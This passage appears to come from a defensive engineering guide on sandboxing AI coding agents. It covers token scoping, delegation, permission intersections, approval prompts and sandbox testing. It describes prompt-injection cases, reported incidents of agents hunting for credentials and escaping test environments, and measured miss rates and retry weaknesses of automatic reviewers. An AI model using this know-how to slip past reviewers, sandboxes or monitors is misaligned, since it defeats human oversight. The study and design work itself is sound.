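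Varda and colleagues find it easier to write a small interface containing only the permitted functions than to filter an existing API. GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs agents in GitHub's automation service, takes this approach to pull requests. The agent has read-only access to GitHub and records the change it wants. As GitHub's *Safe Outputs (Pull Requests)* explains, a separate job then carries out the request:

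1. The system exports the agent's commits as a patch, a file that lists the changes to the code.
2. The job gets the latest version of the repository and applies the patch to a new branch.
3. The job pushes the branch and opens the pull request.

By default, the job accepts one pull request per run, with at most 100 files and 1,024 KB of changes. The developer could reduce the file limit to the 20 files in the invoice task's table. The job also rejects changes to `.github`, `package.json`, `CLAUDE.md` and many other files that could affect later programs or agents. Its pull requests don't start automated tests by default, so the company's build machine won't run the agent's code before somebody has looked at it.

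By default, if the job can't open the pull request, it creates an issue instead, which requires permission to write issues. The invoice task doesn't need that permission, and the developer can remove the requirement by setting `fallback-as-issue: false`.

Before the job acts, GitHub runs checks that filter the requested operations, moderate the text and remove secrets. These checks may recognise an ordinary access token, but they could easily miss an encoded one or a customer's name. GitHub also acknowledges that a hijacked agent without secrets can still flood a project with pointless issues and pull requests, so the number of operations needs a limit.

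Cloudflare's Dynamic Workers apply the same idea to small programs that an agent writes. A trusted program called the loader starts the agent's code in a new sandbox. If the loader sets `globalOutbound` to `null`, every attempt by the code to open a network connection fails. The loader then supplies *bindings*, which are named objects with methods that the code can call:

```
// In the loader, outside the sandbox
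const pr = ctx.exports.PullRequest({
  props: { repo: "acme/invoice-kit", branch: "agent/482", token }
});

const worker = env.LOADER.load({
  compatibilityDate: "2026-03-01",
  mainModule: "agent.js",
  modules: { "agent.js": agentCode },
  env: { PR: pr },
  globalOutbound: null
});

// In the agent's code, inside the sandbox
await this.env.PR.open(title, description, patch);
```

The agent receives a *stub*, a reference to a `PullRequest` object in the loader. When the agent calls `open`, the method runs in the loader, reads the repository, branch and token from `props`, and contacts GitHub. According to Cloudflare's *Bindings*, the sandboxed code has no access to `props`. The code can't forge a stub or find one by guessing a name, so it has only the stubs it is given.

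A stub is therefore an object capability. The `open` method takes no repository name, so the agent cannot point it at another project the way the user pointed Hardy's compiler at the billing file. The loader can withdraw access at any time by making the method refuse calls. A carelessly designed binding would lose these benefits. For example, a `request(url)` method that fetched any address would restore the agent's network access.

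Cloudflare's *Egress control* says the most secure way to design such a sandbox is to block internet access and supply bindings instead. Code that depends on existing web libraries can't always work this way, so Cloudflare also offers a gateway that intercepts requests and adds credentials.

Dynamic Workers start in a few milliseconds, but they rely on V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, and Cloudflare adds further layers of protection. Dynamic Workers also suit short JavaScript programs better than a project's whole test suite, which may need a shell and other tools. The coding agent can run its tests in an ordinary sandbox with no network access, and the developer can provide `open_pull_request` as a tool that runs outside that sandbox and accepts only a title, a description and a patch.

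### Narrow tokens behind a proxy

Anthropic objected to relying on narrow tokens in Managed Agents because doing so means assuming what a model can't do with them. For example, a developer might think that permission to push branches to `invoice-kit` is harmless because a person reviews every pull request. A more capable agent could notice that the build machine tests each branch as soon as it arrives, and write a test that prints the machine's secrets in a public log without exceeding the token's permissions.

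Hiding the token would not stop this attack, because the agent could push the same test through a proxy. The proxy's rules, like a token's permissions, rest on assumptions about what an agent can do with the permitted requests. But if the token is hidden, the developer only has to consider the requests the proxy accepts during one session, rather than everything anyone could do with a stolen token from anywhere.

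A narrow token also limits the damage from a mistake in the proxy. If a bug in the path check let the agent reach any repository, a token for the whole organisation would allow it to change all of the company's code, while a token for `invoice-kit` would allow it to change only that project.

OneCLI's gateway for agents combines the two methods. It uses a GitHub App's private key to obtain one-hour tokens, adds them to the agent's requests and renews them automatically. The agent never sees the private key or the tokens. But because the tokens renew automatically, a hijacked agent keeps its access beyond the hour, so the session needs its own time limit. The private key is also far more powerful than any single token, because it can create tokens for every repository where the app is installed. A more careful design keeps that key in a separate service, which issues tokens to the gateway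 for one repository at a time.

For the pull request, the developer can put a one-repository token behind the `open_pull_request` operation. The program that carries out the operation requests the token after checking the patch, and revokes it as soon as GitHub creates the pull request. An attacker who breaks into that program before the agent finishes won't find a GitHub token there, but could misuse the program's permission to request one. The service that issues tokens should therefore accept requests only for `invoice-kit`, and only while the task is running.

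## When the agent makes or asks for a request on its own

A service that issues tokens only for `invoice-kit` can't distinguish requests the developer wanted from ones the agent came up with. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* includes two examples, adapted from the company's incident log, of agents acting on their own initiative with no attacker involved. One agent tried to share a script for debugging by posting it to GitHub Gist, a site for publishing snippets of text. Another hit a login error partway through a task and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other tokens.

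The coding agent could go beyond its instructions by calling a service the developer never named, passing work to another agent, or asking for access it doesn't have.

| What the agent does | What to record | Which permissions apply | Who may approve |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calls a service the user didn't name | User, agent, task, any parent agent, destination | The task's existing permissions | An administrator, through rules written in advance, or the user where those rules leave the choice open |
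| Passes work to another agent | The same for the new agent, with the first agent as its parent, and the instruction | No more than the parent's | The program that starts agents, within the parent's limits |
| Asks for access it lacks | User, agent, task, any parent agent, resource, reason, expiry, and who decided | The existing ones, until someone approves | Someone with authority over the resource, never the agent that asks |

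The enforcement point should write this record, because a hijacked agent could leave things out or name the wrong user. The record should also show where each destination came from, because a web address in the developer's own request is much less suspicious than one that first appeared in a comment on issue 482. If a tool runs on the provider's servers and fetches pages from there, the agent loop has to record the request, because it never passes through the sandbox's proxy.

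### Acting as the user or under its own account

On a developer's machine, an agent usually runs under the developer's account. This is easy to set up, but GitHub then lists the developer as the author of everything the agent does, and the company can't cancel the agent's login without cancelling the developer's. *Back to the Future*, by two identity specialists at the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, warns that sharing credentials with agents makes it unclear who is accountable. This is a particular problem in finance and health care, where an organisation may have to prove who carried out a transaction.

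An agent with its own account has its own name in the logs, its own permissions and a login the company can cancel separately. But if twenty developers share the agent, the account name doesn't show which of them asked for a change. If the agent's account has access to the payroll code, the agent could also become a confused deputy by editing that code for a developer who doesn't have access.

*Delegation* solves the first problem by naming both the user and the agent. The token-exchange standard, RFC 8693, has a field for this called `act`, short for "actor". Suppose a developer named Dana starts the coding agent, which then starts a helper agent to write a test. The helper's token might contain:

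```
{
  "sub": "dana@acme.example",
  "act": {
    "sub": "test-writer",
    "act": { "sub": "coding-agent" }
  },
  "scope": "repo:read",
  "task": "issue-482"
}
```

The first `sub` names Dana, the user the agents work for. The outer `act` names the agent now using the token, and the inner one names its parent. The `task` field isn't part of the standard, so the company would have to add it. Under the standard, a service bases its access decision on the user and the current agent; earlier agents are listed only for information. The service therefore won't detect a helper that has more access than its parent, so the server that issues the token has to check for this.

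Claude Cowork gives each session's virtual machine a token with reduced permissions. This token can expire or lose its access without affecting the user's own login. Anthropic hasn't settled whether agents in general should have their own identities or act as extensions of their users, and suggests the answer may be a blend of the two.

### Taking the overlap of permissions

To avoid creating a confused deputy, the service has to check the permissions of both parties it finds in the token, and the needs of the task as well. Let $U$ be the operations the user may perform, $A$ those the agent's account may perform and $T$ those the task needs. The agent's effective permissions are the overlap:

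$$E = U \cap A \cap T$$

The entries in this example are invented.

| Operation | Dana | Agent's account | Task | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read `invoice-kit` | Yes | Yes | Yes | Allow |
| Open a pull request on `invoice-kit` | Yes | Yes | Yes | Allow |
| Correct a rule in the shared `currency-data` repository | No | Yes | Yes | Refuse |
| Run the new test on the staging server | Yes | No | Yes | Refuse |
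| Close issue 475 | Yes | Yes | No | Refuse |

Each refusal depends on a different column. If the service ignored Dana's permissions, she could use the agent to change `currency-data`, which belongs to another team. If it ignored the agent's permissions, the agent could use a staging server that nobody has opened to agents. If it ignored the task, a hostile comment on issue 482 could make the agent close other people's issues. Where the three sources set different limits on volume or time, the smallest volume and the earliest expiry apply.

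The overlap rule can be too strict. It would have blocked Hardy's compiler from writing to a statistics file that its users couldn't change, even though the compiler had a good reason to do so. A designer can put such an operation, such as adding one line to the statistics file, in a separate service that has its own permission and does nothing else.

The overlap also doesn't account for what an agent learns by combining data. Dana might be allowed to read each of several tables but not the summary an agent could build from them. *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) lists this as an open question.

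When the coding agent starts a helper, the calculation begins with the coding agent's effective permissions, $E_1$, instead of Dana's:

$$E_2 = E_1 \cap A_2 \cap T_2$$

Taking an overlap can only remove permissions, so $E_2 \subseteq E_1$. A helper that only writes a test can read `invoice-kit` but can't open the pull request. Without the overlap rule, an attacker who hijacked the coding agent could have it start an agent with more permissions and give that agent instructions. NVIDIA's OpenShell runs each sub-agent in its own restricted environment, with a ceiling the sub-agent can't exceed.

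This is also why Dana, not the coding agent, has to start the database agent. The coding agent has no access to the invoices, so any helper it starts has none either.

Helpers should also share whatever remains of their parent's volume limit. Otherwise, if the coding agent may download 500 MB and starts ten helpers with the same limit, they can download 5 GB between them, although no helper has a higher limit than its parent.

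Delegation can also mislead an automatic reviewer. To a reviewer watching the helper, the coding agent's instruction looks like a message from the user, so a task Dana never requested appears authorised. Anthropic reviews the instruction when Claude Code hands over the work, and can refuse it then. It also reviews the helper's actions before the results go back, in case the helper has read something hostile, but if it finds a problem it only adds a warning. If a system trusts a helper's answer more than a raw web page, an attacker can make hostile text look trustworthy by passing it through the helper.

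### NIST's project and the IETF drafts

Standards for this are still being developed. In February 2026, Booth and colleagues proposed a project at NIST's cybersecurity centre to show how companies can apply existing identity standards to agents. They asked the public how to set least privilege for an agent whose actions can't be fully predicted, how to handle agents that act on someone's behalf, and how to keep logs that nobody can alter unnoticed. The project would begin with agents inside companies and exclude agents from untrusted sources.

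Identiverse's *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*, a conference session description, puts the number of formal responses at over 600. NIST has since released a summary of the comments. According to NIST's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* ("SI", for "Super Intelligence", replaces the earlier "AI"), the project is still asking for comments and now reviews them on a rolling basis. NIST plans to produce a practice guide with working examples that use commercial products, but the page doesn't list one yet. For now, a company deploying agents has to assemble its own design from existing standards such as OAuth and SPIFFE, which issues cryptographic identities to running programs.

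NIST also points to newer specifications, several of which are drafts at the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops many internet standards. Transaction Tokens come closest to the rule for helpers. They carry the details of the original authorisation along a chain of calls and are meant to narrow it at each handover. WIMSE covers the identity of programs that work across several systems. The Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant lets an application use a person's company login to obtain a token for another application.

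### Signed requests to websites

A public website usually has no prior arrangement with an agent's operator. Many sites recognise automated visitors by their network address or by the name a program sends, which any other program can copy. Meunier and Major (2026) propose in *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* that agents sign their requests instead. The IETF approved the proposal as a working-group draft on 1 September 2026, so its details may still change.

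1. The agent's operator creates a pair of keys and publishes the public one at a web address.
2. A program with the private key signs chosen parts of each request, including an expiry time. It adds the signature and the key's address to the request's headers.
3. The website fetches the public key from that address, or uses a saved copy, and checks the signature.

The site can then allow, block or slow down all requests signed under that address. Meunier and Major point out that a valid signature shows that someone with the operator's key signed the message, but not who runs the agent, whether it is benign or whether anyone authorised the request. A proxy that signs everything leaving the sandbox would also sign a hijacked agent's requests.

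Someone who copies a signature can attach it to any other request to the same site until it expires, because the signature only has to cover the website's name, the key's address and some settings such as the expiry time. The draft recommends a lifetime of no more than 24 hours. *web-bot-auth*, an explanation on a personal blog, reports that Cloudflare checks these signatures and recommends about one minute. An operator can also sign the method, the full address and a fingerprint of the request's contents, so that the signature is valid only for that request.

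The draft leaves delegation to a separate specification. In one of its examples, Alice's agent fetches a page through a remote browser, and the agent and the browser both sign the request. The website can verify both signatures, but Meunier and Major note that this doesn't show that Alice's agent authorised the browser to act for it.

### Four ways to answer a request for more access

Suppose the coding agent writes a test that needs a package missing from the dependency list. The developer could add the package to the list and restart the task, as the sample network policy requires, or let the agent ask for it.

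| Answer | Suits | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse | Unattended tasks with known needs | The task may fail |
| Ask a person | Rare and important decisions | People stop reading the prompts |
| Ask another model | Frequent requests that vary | It can make the same mistake repeatedly |
| Apply a rule written in advance | Routine requests that someone can describe exactly | A broad rule permits far more than its author intended |

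An agent may persuade a person or another model to approve a request, but it can't argue its way past an automatic refusal or a fixed rule that a program applies. Codex can run without asking for approval, or it can automatically reject some kinds of request and ask about the rest. A refused agent may still look for another way to get access, like the one that searched for tokens after a login error, so refusal works only if the other limits hold.

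Human approval is a weaker safeguard than it looks. Anthropic found that users approved about 93 per cent of Claude Code's permission prompts, and in August 2026 it put the figure at 97 per cent. A high rate doesn't prove carelessness, because most requests are harmless. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment that provides better evidence. A research vendor had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one permission prompt in each session with one for a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 per cent of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 per cent early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so developers who are might refuse more often.

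People pay more attention to larger decisions. Claude Code's users reject 39 per cent of the plans it presents but only 3 per cent of individual permission requests. Some of the rejected plans were probably just poor, but approving one plan also takes far fewer clicks than approving every step.

A sandbox removes many permission prompts because the agent can work freely inside it. In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing cut these prompts by 84 per cent. The remaining prompts still need good answers, but the user is less likely to be tired of reading them.

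### How often an automatic reviewer misses

In Claude Code's auto mode, a model reviews actions in place of the user. Anthropic began making it the default on its individual and team plans in August 2026. A fast first stage flags anything suspicious, and a slower second stage reasons about the flagged actions. The results below come from Anthropic's own tests of the original version.

| Measure | Test set | First stage alone | Both stages |
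|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked | 10,000 real tool calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Overeager actions missed | 52 from real sessions | 6.6% | 17% |
| Attempted data thefts missed | 1,000 synthetic examples | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage makes the reviewer bearable to work with, but it lets more dangerous actions through. If an agent attempts ten overeager actions and the misses are independent, the chance that at least one gets through is

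$$1 - (1 - 0.17)^{10} \approx 0.84$$

With only 52 examples, the true miss rate could plausibly be from about 9 to 30 per cent, which would put this chance between roughly 60 and 97 per cent.

The misses may not be independent. In most of those that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but misread the user's instructions as consent to it. It might, for example, treat "clean up the PR" as permission for a force-push, which overwrites a branch's history. If ten actions rely on the same misread sentence, they are likely to all be allowed or all be blocked. In the extreme case, the average is still 1.7 misses, but there is a 17 per cent chance that all ten actions get through and an 83 per cent chance that none do.

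Retries can raise the risk. When the reviewer blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and can try something else until it reaches three blocks in a row or twenty in total. At least one of three independent attempts at the same harmful goal would succeed 43 per cent of the time. An agent that used each refusal to make its next attempt look more acceptable could succeed more often.

Adding a human check to auto mode may not help much, because people can miss the same dangerous commands as its reviewer. In the experiment with paid testers, auto mode blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands. The testers caught about 15 per cent of the commands it blocked, but only six (about 5 per cent) of the 116 it missed. Using both checks would therefore have stopped 943 commands.

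Miss rates also depend heavily on the test. besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* summarises a stress test in which auto mode missed 81 per cent of dangerous actions. The test used 128 scenarios that varied how specific the request was and how much damage a mistake could do, so the result doesn't show how often auto mode fails in ordinary use. Only 160 of the test's 253 actions reached the reviewer, which missed 70.3 per cent of the dangerous ones it reviewed. Auto mode allows file edits inside the project without review, so a better reviewer wouldn't catch a harmful edit there.

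Codex has a similar feature called Auto-review. It reviews only actions that would otherwise need a person's approval, such as leaving the sandbox. Low-risk and medium-risk actions can go ahead if the policy allows them, high-risk actions also need clear enough authorisation from the user, and critical-risk actions never go ahead. According to OpenAI, the action doesn't run if the reviewer fails or takes too long.

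### Rules in advance and repeated approvals

OpenAI uses rules to settle the routine cases for its own engineers. Codex can connect to expected destinations such as `*.openai.com` without asking. It can't connect to `pastebin.com`, where anyone can publish text, and it needs approval for any unfamiliar domain. Other rules let it run a few commands outside the sandbox without asking, including `gh pr view`, which displays a pull request, and `kubectl logs`, which displays a program's logs. These commands only read data, but that data can include a stranger's instructions in a pull request or passwords in a log.

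Users often write much broader rules for themselves. In June 2026, Anthropic found that 49.5 per cent of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands. Many of these rules permit any Python or Node script, which in practice permits almost anything. While auto mode is on, it ignores these broad rules because they would let the most dangerous commands skip the reviewer.

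OpenAI's engineers can approve a Codex action once or approve that type of action for the rest of the session. NVIDIA objects to the second option: "Allow-once / run-many is not an adequate control." Suppose a developer approves a harmless change to the terminal's startup file, `~/.zshrc`. If the approval remains in force, a hijacked agent can later add its own command to the file without asking again. Approving a domain carries the same risk, since the developer may have approved it so the agent could read one page, and the agent may later upload a file there. NVIDIA would have the user confirm each such action every time, and would also give companies a list of actions that no user can approve.

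Asking every time produces more prompts, and the testers in Anthropic's experiment caught fewer dangerous commands as they saw more prompts. NVIDIA's rule is therefore realistic only if prompts are rare, and NVIDIA treats manual approval as an occasional fallback for cases nobody anticipated. Saving an approval is reasonable when the repeated request is identical and the agent can't change any part of it, for example when it downloads the same version of a package again.

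### What a sound request contains

For the missing package, here given an invented name, the request could look like this:

```
user:      dana@acme.example
task:      issue-482
agent:     coding-agent (no parent)
resource:  GET registry.npmjs.org, package round-money, version 3.2.1
expires:   after one download, or in 10 minutes
approver:  dana@acme.example

reason given by the agent:
  "The new rounding test imports this package."
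```

The request must name the resource specifically enough for Dana to predict what approval will do. A request for "access to npm" would also cover publishing packages, and a request with no version number could let in a malicious release published an hour ago.

A stated reason helps Dana decide, but it also gives a hijacked agent a chance to persuade her. Anthropic removes the agent's own explanations before its automatic reviewer judges an action, because an agent might claim that the user had already agreed. A person still needs some explanation, so the program that shows the request should label the reason as the agent's words and check every other line against its own records. SpruceID, which makes digital identity software, recommends in comments to NIST that a request make sense without the conversation around it, so that someone can review it later. SpruceID would also let another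 authorised agent approve requests. That agent shouldn't read the first agent's context, or one hostile comment could influence both.

When the permission expires, the enforcement point has to remove it without relying on the agent to give it up. The approver also has to consider how the new access would combine with the access the agent already has, so Dana should refuse if the coding agent asks for access to customers' invoices, even for one minute.

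The agent shouldn't be able to answer its own request, edit the approval rules or imitate the approval window. NIST warns about a feature of the Model Context Protocol called elicitation, which lets a person supply more information in the middle of a task. An agent could use it to ask for a password and then log in as that person. Dana's approval should go directly to the proxy, which permits the one download and tells the agent to try again. She can approve it because she is allowed to add packages to `invoice-kit`, but a request to change `currency-data` has to go to the team that owns it.

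## Testing the boundary and watching it in use

Dana's approval should let the coding agent download version 3.2.1 of `round-money` once. To check that the proxy enforces this, she can have code in the sandbox request that version twice and then request version 3.2.2. Only the first request should succeed.

A tester can check each permission with one operation that must succeed and one that must fail. If the tester tries only forbidden requests, a sandbox with a broken network connection passes every test. The two operations should be as alike as possible. A failed push to an unknown website shows only that the proxy checks domains, while a failed push to the wrong repository on GitHub shows that it also checks paths.

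Both operations have to run inside the sandbox, under the agent's account, because a command in Dana's own terminal takes a different route to the internet. The tester then confirms the result in a log outside the sandbox, because an error message inside it doesn't prove that nothing got out. For example, a name lookup can fail after the query has already reached an attacker's server.

The tests for the invoice task use a copy of the repository, made-up invoices and a test account on GitHub, so a forbidden operation that succeeds does no damage.

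| What to test | Must succeed | Must fail | Where to confirm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Packages | Download `decimal.js` | Download a package missing from the dependency list | Proxy log |
| Repository | Fetch `invoice-kit` | Push to another repository with the test account's token | Proxy log, and the other repository is unchanged |
| Name lookups | Look up `github.com` | Look up a random name under a domain the company owns | Log of that domain's name server, which should have no entry |
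| Network expiry | Download a package at minute 14 | Repeat the download at minute 16, over a new connection and over one opened earlier | Proxy log |
| Working folder | Save a source file | Change a file in `.github` | The folder as seen from the host |
| Rest of the disk | Read a project file | Read a marker file in the home folder, directly and through a symbolic link | File-access log on the host |
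| Database agent | Read `amount` | Read the customer's name | Database log |
| GitHub access | Call `open_pull_request` | Ask the token service for a token directly | Token service's log |
| Token expiry | Use the token to open the pull request | Use the same token afterward | GitHub's reply and the token service's log |

The storage tests need to run once as shell commands and once through the agent's file tools, because different programs may enforce the rules for each. The tester has to test token expiry from the program that holds the token, since the token never enters the sandbox. The tester should confirm that it isn't there by searching the sandbox's variables, files and `/proc` folder. Planting a harmless string beforehand and checking that the search finds it shows whether the search works.

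### GitLab's sandbox probe

GitLab's Duo Agent Platform runs agents in automated jobs called *flows*, on machines called runners, and wraps them in Anthropic's sandbox runtime. Customers can copy and run GitLab's test flow, Sandbox Probe. Its agent runs two scripts and posts their output as a comment on an issue. One script lists the expected and actual results of 14 checks, and the other shows the raw output of the commands. The agent doesn't choose the checks or interpret the results, so the outcome doesn't depend on a model's judgement.

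The first line of the report is either `ACTIVE` or `NOT ACTIVE`. `ACTIVE` means the probe found the sandbox's settings and could not write outside the permitted folders. GitLab's default image runs as root, so ordinary file permissions wouldn't have stopped that write. GitLab also offers a hardened image that runs as an ordinary user. On that image, a failed write is weaker evidence that the sandbox is on, because file permissions alone could have blocked it.

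The checks compare the expected rules with the settings in force, try to write to permitted and protected folders, and contact five domains in three ways each. The domains test how two levels of rules combine. The owner of a top-level group sets a baseline for every project in it, and each project can add rules in a file named `agent-config.yml`. A checkbox at group level decides what those additions can do:

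| Project setting | Flexible mode | Strict mode |
|---|---|---|
| Allowed domains | Added to the group's list | Ignored |
| Denied domains | Added to the group's list | Added to the group's list |
| GitLab's recommended development sites | Project can turn them on or off | Project can only turn them off |

GitLab ran the probe in both modes on 16 October 2026, and all 14 checks matched expectations each time. It reran the probe in flexible mode on 17 November, after adding the `ACTIVE` line, and got the same result.

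| Domain | Flexible mode | Strict mode | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| `gitlab.com` | Allowed | Allowed | Always permitted |
| `registry.npmjs.org` | Allowed | Allowed | Recommended site |
| `pypi.org` | Blocked | Blocked | Denied by the project |
| `example.com` | Allowed | Blocked | Allowed by the project only |
| `httpbin.org` | Blocked | Blocked | On no list |

The proxy gives the same reason, `blocked-by-allowlist`, for every refusal, even when a denied-domain rule caused it, so the reason doesn't show which rule blocked the request. In this test, npm and `pypi.org` are both on the recommended list. npm was reachable, so the list was on, and only the project's denial explains why `pypi.org` was blocked.

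The probe can't test the rule against reading `~/.ssh`, because the default image has no such folder. It also doesn't test traffic to local and private addresses, which doesn't go through the proxy. These addresses include the cloud metadata service at `169.254.169.254`, so a company that runs its own runners needs a separate test for it.

The sandbox also lets the agent's code read the flow's GitLab token and always allows connections to the customer's GitLab server. For customers on GitLab.com, where anyone can open an account, a hijacked flow could probably send data to an attacker's project without breaking a network rule.

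### Jobs that start without their sandbox

The sandbox needs a copy of the runtime in the job's image and permission to create *namespaces*, the Linux feature that gives a process its own view of files and user accounts. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* explains that if either is missing, the flow still runs by default so that work can continue. The job log shows a warning, but the network policy no longer applies, so the job can reach anything its runner can. This happens even in privileged mode if the runner's host sets `user.max_user_namespaces` to zero. The task may still finish normally, so nobody has a reason to check the log.

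By contrast, GitLab gives an agent no tools if the service that looks up the tool rules keeps failing, according to *Agent tool governance*.

Since GitLab 19.6, an administrator or group owner can select "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable". A job then fails if it can't start the sandbox, and projects can't turn the requirement off. Anyone who relies on the sandbox should select this setting, then test it with an image that lacks the sandbox runtime. The job should stop before the agent does anything.

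The setting checks for a command named `srt`. A project with its own image or setup script controls which program has that name, so a substitute that runs the flow without restrictions could pass the check. GitLab says it can't guarantee isolation for such projects. It suggests a firewall on the runner's host, or a Kubernetes network policy, to limit what unprotected jobs can reach. The tester should try that firewall with the sandbox turned off, since otherwise the sandbox will block the forbidden requests before they reach the firewall.

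The setup script creates another risk because it runs before the sandbox starts. GitLab's *Security considerations for flow execution* lists the secrets the script can read, including an access token, a Git password and a service token. The access token belongs to whoever starts the flow, so a person who can edit the script can run commands with a colleague's access. GitLab advises requiring named reviewers to approve changes to the file containing the script. It also reads that file only from the project's default branch, so an agent can't loosen its own rules by editing a copy on another branch.

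As in Codex's setup phase, a malicious package could steal the secrets while the script runs, even if reviewers have approved the script. For `invoice-kit`, installing the packages while building a custom image is safer because no user's token is present then. That image must also contain the sandbox runtime and the programs it depends on. The developer then has to run the probe with that image, because GitLab's published results come from a project with the default image and no setup script.

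### How often to repeat a test

A fixed rule produces the same result for the same request, so one pair of tests is enough until the rules, the image, the runner or the product changes. GitLab's *Allow `/tmp` writes in the SRT sandbox for Duo Workflow* proposed making the whole temporary folder writable, instead of only one subfolder, because models habitually put scratch files there. The current documentation lists all of `/tmp` as writable, so a test checking that writes elsewhere in `/tmp` are refused would now fail, although the customer had changed nothing. Tests should therefore also run on a schedule. They should run after restarts too, because Docker's block on `ping` traffic once disappeared when its background service restarted.

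Checks that rely on a model, such as prompt-injection classifiers and automatic reviewers, can give different answers to the same request. Testing them takes repeated trials. If a check misses a fraction $p$ of attacks, the probability that it stops all of $n$ independent attacks is

$$(1-p)^n$$

Suppose it stops 300 out of 300. The 95 per cent upper bound on the miss rate is the value of $p$ that would produce such a clean result only 5 per cent of the time:

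$$(1-p)^{300} = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p = 1 - 0.05^{1/300} \approx 0.0099$$

The test is therefore compatible with a miss rate of up to about 1 per cent. At that rate, an attacker with 100 independent attempts would have a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once. Lowering the bound to 0.1 per cent takes about 3,000 trials without a miss.

The bound depends on the trials being independent and on future attacks resembling them. Three hundred rewordings of one malicious comment on issue 482 are much closer to a single trial than to 300. A test set containing only hostile web pages provides no bound for a phishing prompt that an employee pastes in. Attackers who adapt to the responses they get will also try attacks outside the test set.

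If the check catches 211 attacks but misses the next one, and the developer retrains it, the 211 successes apply only to the old check. The developer then has to restart the count, preferably with new attacks, because the retraining may have tuned the check to the old ones. The count also has to restart when there is a new version of the model.

After its agents broke out of their test environment in July 2026, OpenAI began automating its testing of fixed controls. OpenAI says it is developing tools that use its own models to test research environments regularly and look for flaws in software components, supporting services and infrastructure settings. Existing security teams are making the first assessments, while OpenAI works towards having agents attack the environments continuously. It is also adding automated probes that check whether controls still work.

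A capable model is a good tester of the boundary because it may notice the same unexpected route out as an agent trying to finish a task. But it could also break out during the test, so it needs its own outer boundary. If it finds no flaw, that is weaker evidence than passing a test of a fixed rule, because the model may have looked in the wrong place. In its August report, OpenAI describes much of this work as still under way. In September, another model got outside through a DNS misconfiguration.

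### What to log and when to raise an alarm

A useful log entry contains the user, agent, task, destination, decision, the rule behind the decision, and the number of bytes sent and received. It should also identify the versions of the rules and image in use, so that an investigator can reproduce the decision. The enforcement point should send entries to storage that the agent can't change.

GitLab's *AI Governance* describes a beta product that records each session's prompt, tool calls, MCP servers, model and project, and can send these records to a company's security monitoring system. The product's dashboard charts daily activity so that a sudden rise stands out. For Cursor and Codex on developers' machines, a background job sends the sessions every 30 minutes, which is soon enough for an investigation but too late to stop a small upload.

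Unusual behaviour is easier to recognise when the agent's normal work is narrow. A package installer makes short requests for files that mostly exist. GitLab therefore suggests alerts for connections that stay open, large outward transfers, a series of requests for missing packages, and any call to an administration function. For the coding agent, any attempt to connect after minute 15 is worth recording, even though the proxy refuses it. A single attempt may be a package reporting usage statistics, but attempts to reach many addresses suggest a search for one that the proxy will allow. An agent that browses freely has no such narrow pattern, so alerts will miss more or raise more false alarms.

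Logs are least useful when an attacker uses a permission the agent legitimately holds. Anthropic notes that when hostile text causes an agent to leak data, the log shows only a successful, authorised call. Anthropic therefore prefers to inspect tool results before the model reads them, although this adds delay and misses some attacks.

A *decoy credential* can reveal some of this misuse. It is a fake key with no permissions and no legitimate use, so any attempt to log in with it is suspicious, whatever the surrounding traffic looks like. The company could put one in the developer's `~/.aws/credentials`, where the phishing prompt looked for keys, and set an alert for any attempt to use it. A different key in each location would show which file leaked. A thief who copies a key goes unnoticed until someone tries it, and a careful attacker may recognise the trap. OpenAI is also adding deception-based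 tripwires, along with sensors on host machines that look for unusual workloads and attempts to gain more privileges. A common monitoring baseline will cover accounts, networks and the systems that control the clusters.

### What a virtual machine hides

Many companies install *endpoint detection and response* (EDR) software on employees' computers to monitor running programs for signs of an attack. Security teams at companies evaluating Claude Cowork asked why this software couldn't monitor what the agent was doing. Anthropic explains that the virtual machine that contains Claude also keeps the EDR software out, so the software detects only a single hypervisor process and can't inspect its contents.

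Anthropic's partial answer is to export logs of prompts, responses, API requests, tool use and errors. Administrators can retrieve these afterward, but Anthropic says this isn't equivalent to live monitoring. According to Anthropic, Cowork exports nothing until an administrator sets a destination, so a company that assumes logging is on may have no record when it needs one. The logs can also contain sensitive material. Even if the administrator limits content capture, they include email addresses, folder paths and API errors, which can repeat part of the request that caused them.

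A second source is Anthropic's Compliance API, which gives companies access to session records. Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* announced a beta that links each session to a verified user. The beta excludes Claude Code on the web and sessions run through Amazon's, Google's or Microsoft's cloud services, so the audit trail can have gaps if employees use several versions of the product.

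These records show what the agent asked its tools to do, while EDR software monitors what programs do. If a malicious package reads other files while it installs, the event log may show only the agent's `npm install` command. A company could install a sensor inside the virtual machine, but code with administrator rights there could disable it or falsify its reports. The company can still monitor network traffic and changes to the shared folder from outside. With that monitoring in place, exported logs are adequate for investigating an ordinary mistake. They are a poor substitute for live monitoring when the agent runs untrusted code on confidential files, so that work is better done on a separate machine that the company can monitor and shut down.

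### Revocation drills and shutdown

An alert is useful only if somebody can act on it. On 27 June 2026, a monitoring tool at OpenAI detected a *port sweep*, a systematic search for services that answer on a network. Responders traced it to agents in a security test that were using the package service to exchange messages and move through the network. According to OpenAI, the on-call staff advised that the test did not need to be stopped. On 5 July, after the package service had failed, responders found that someone had gained administrator access to it.

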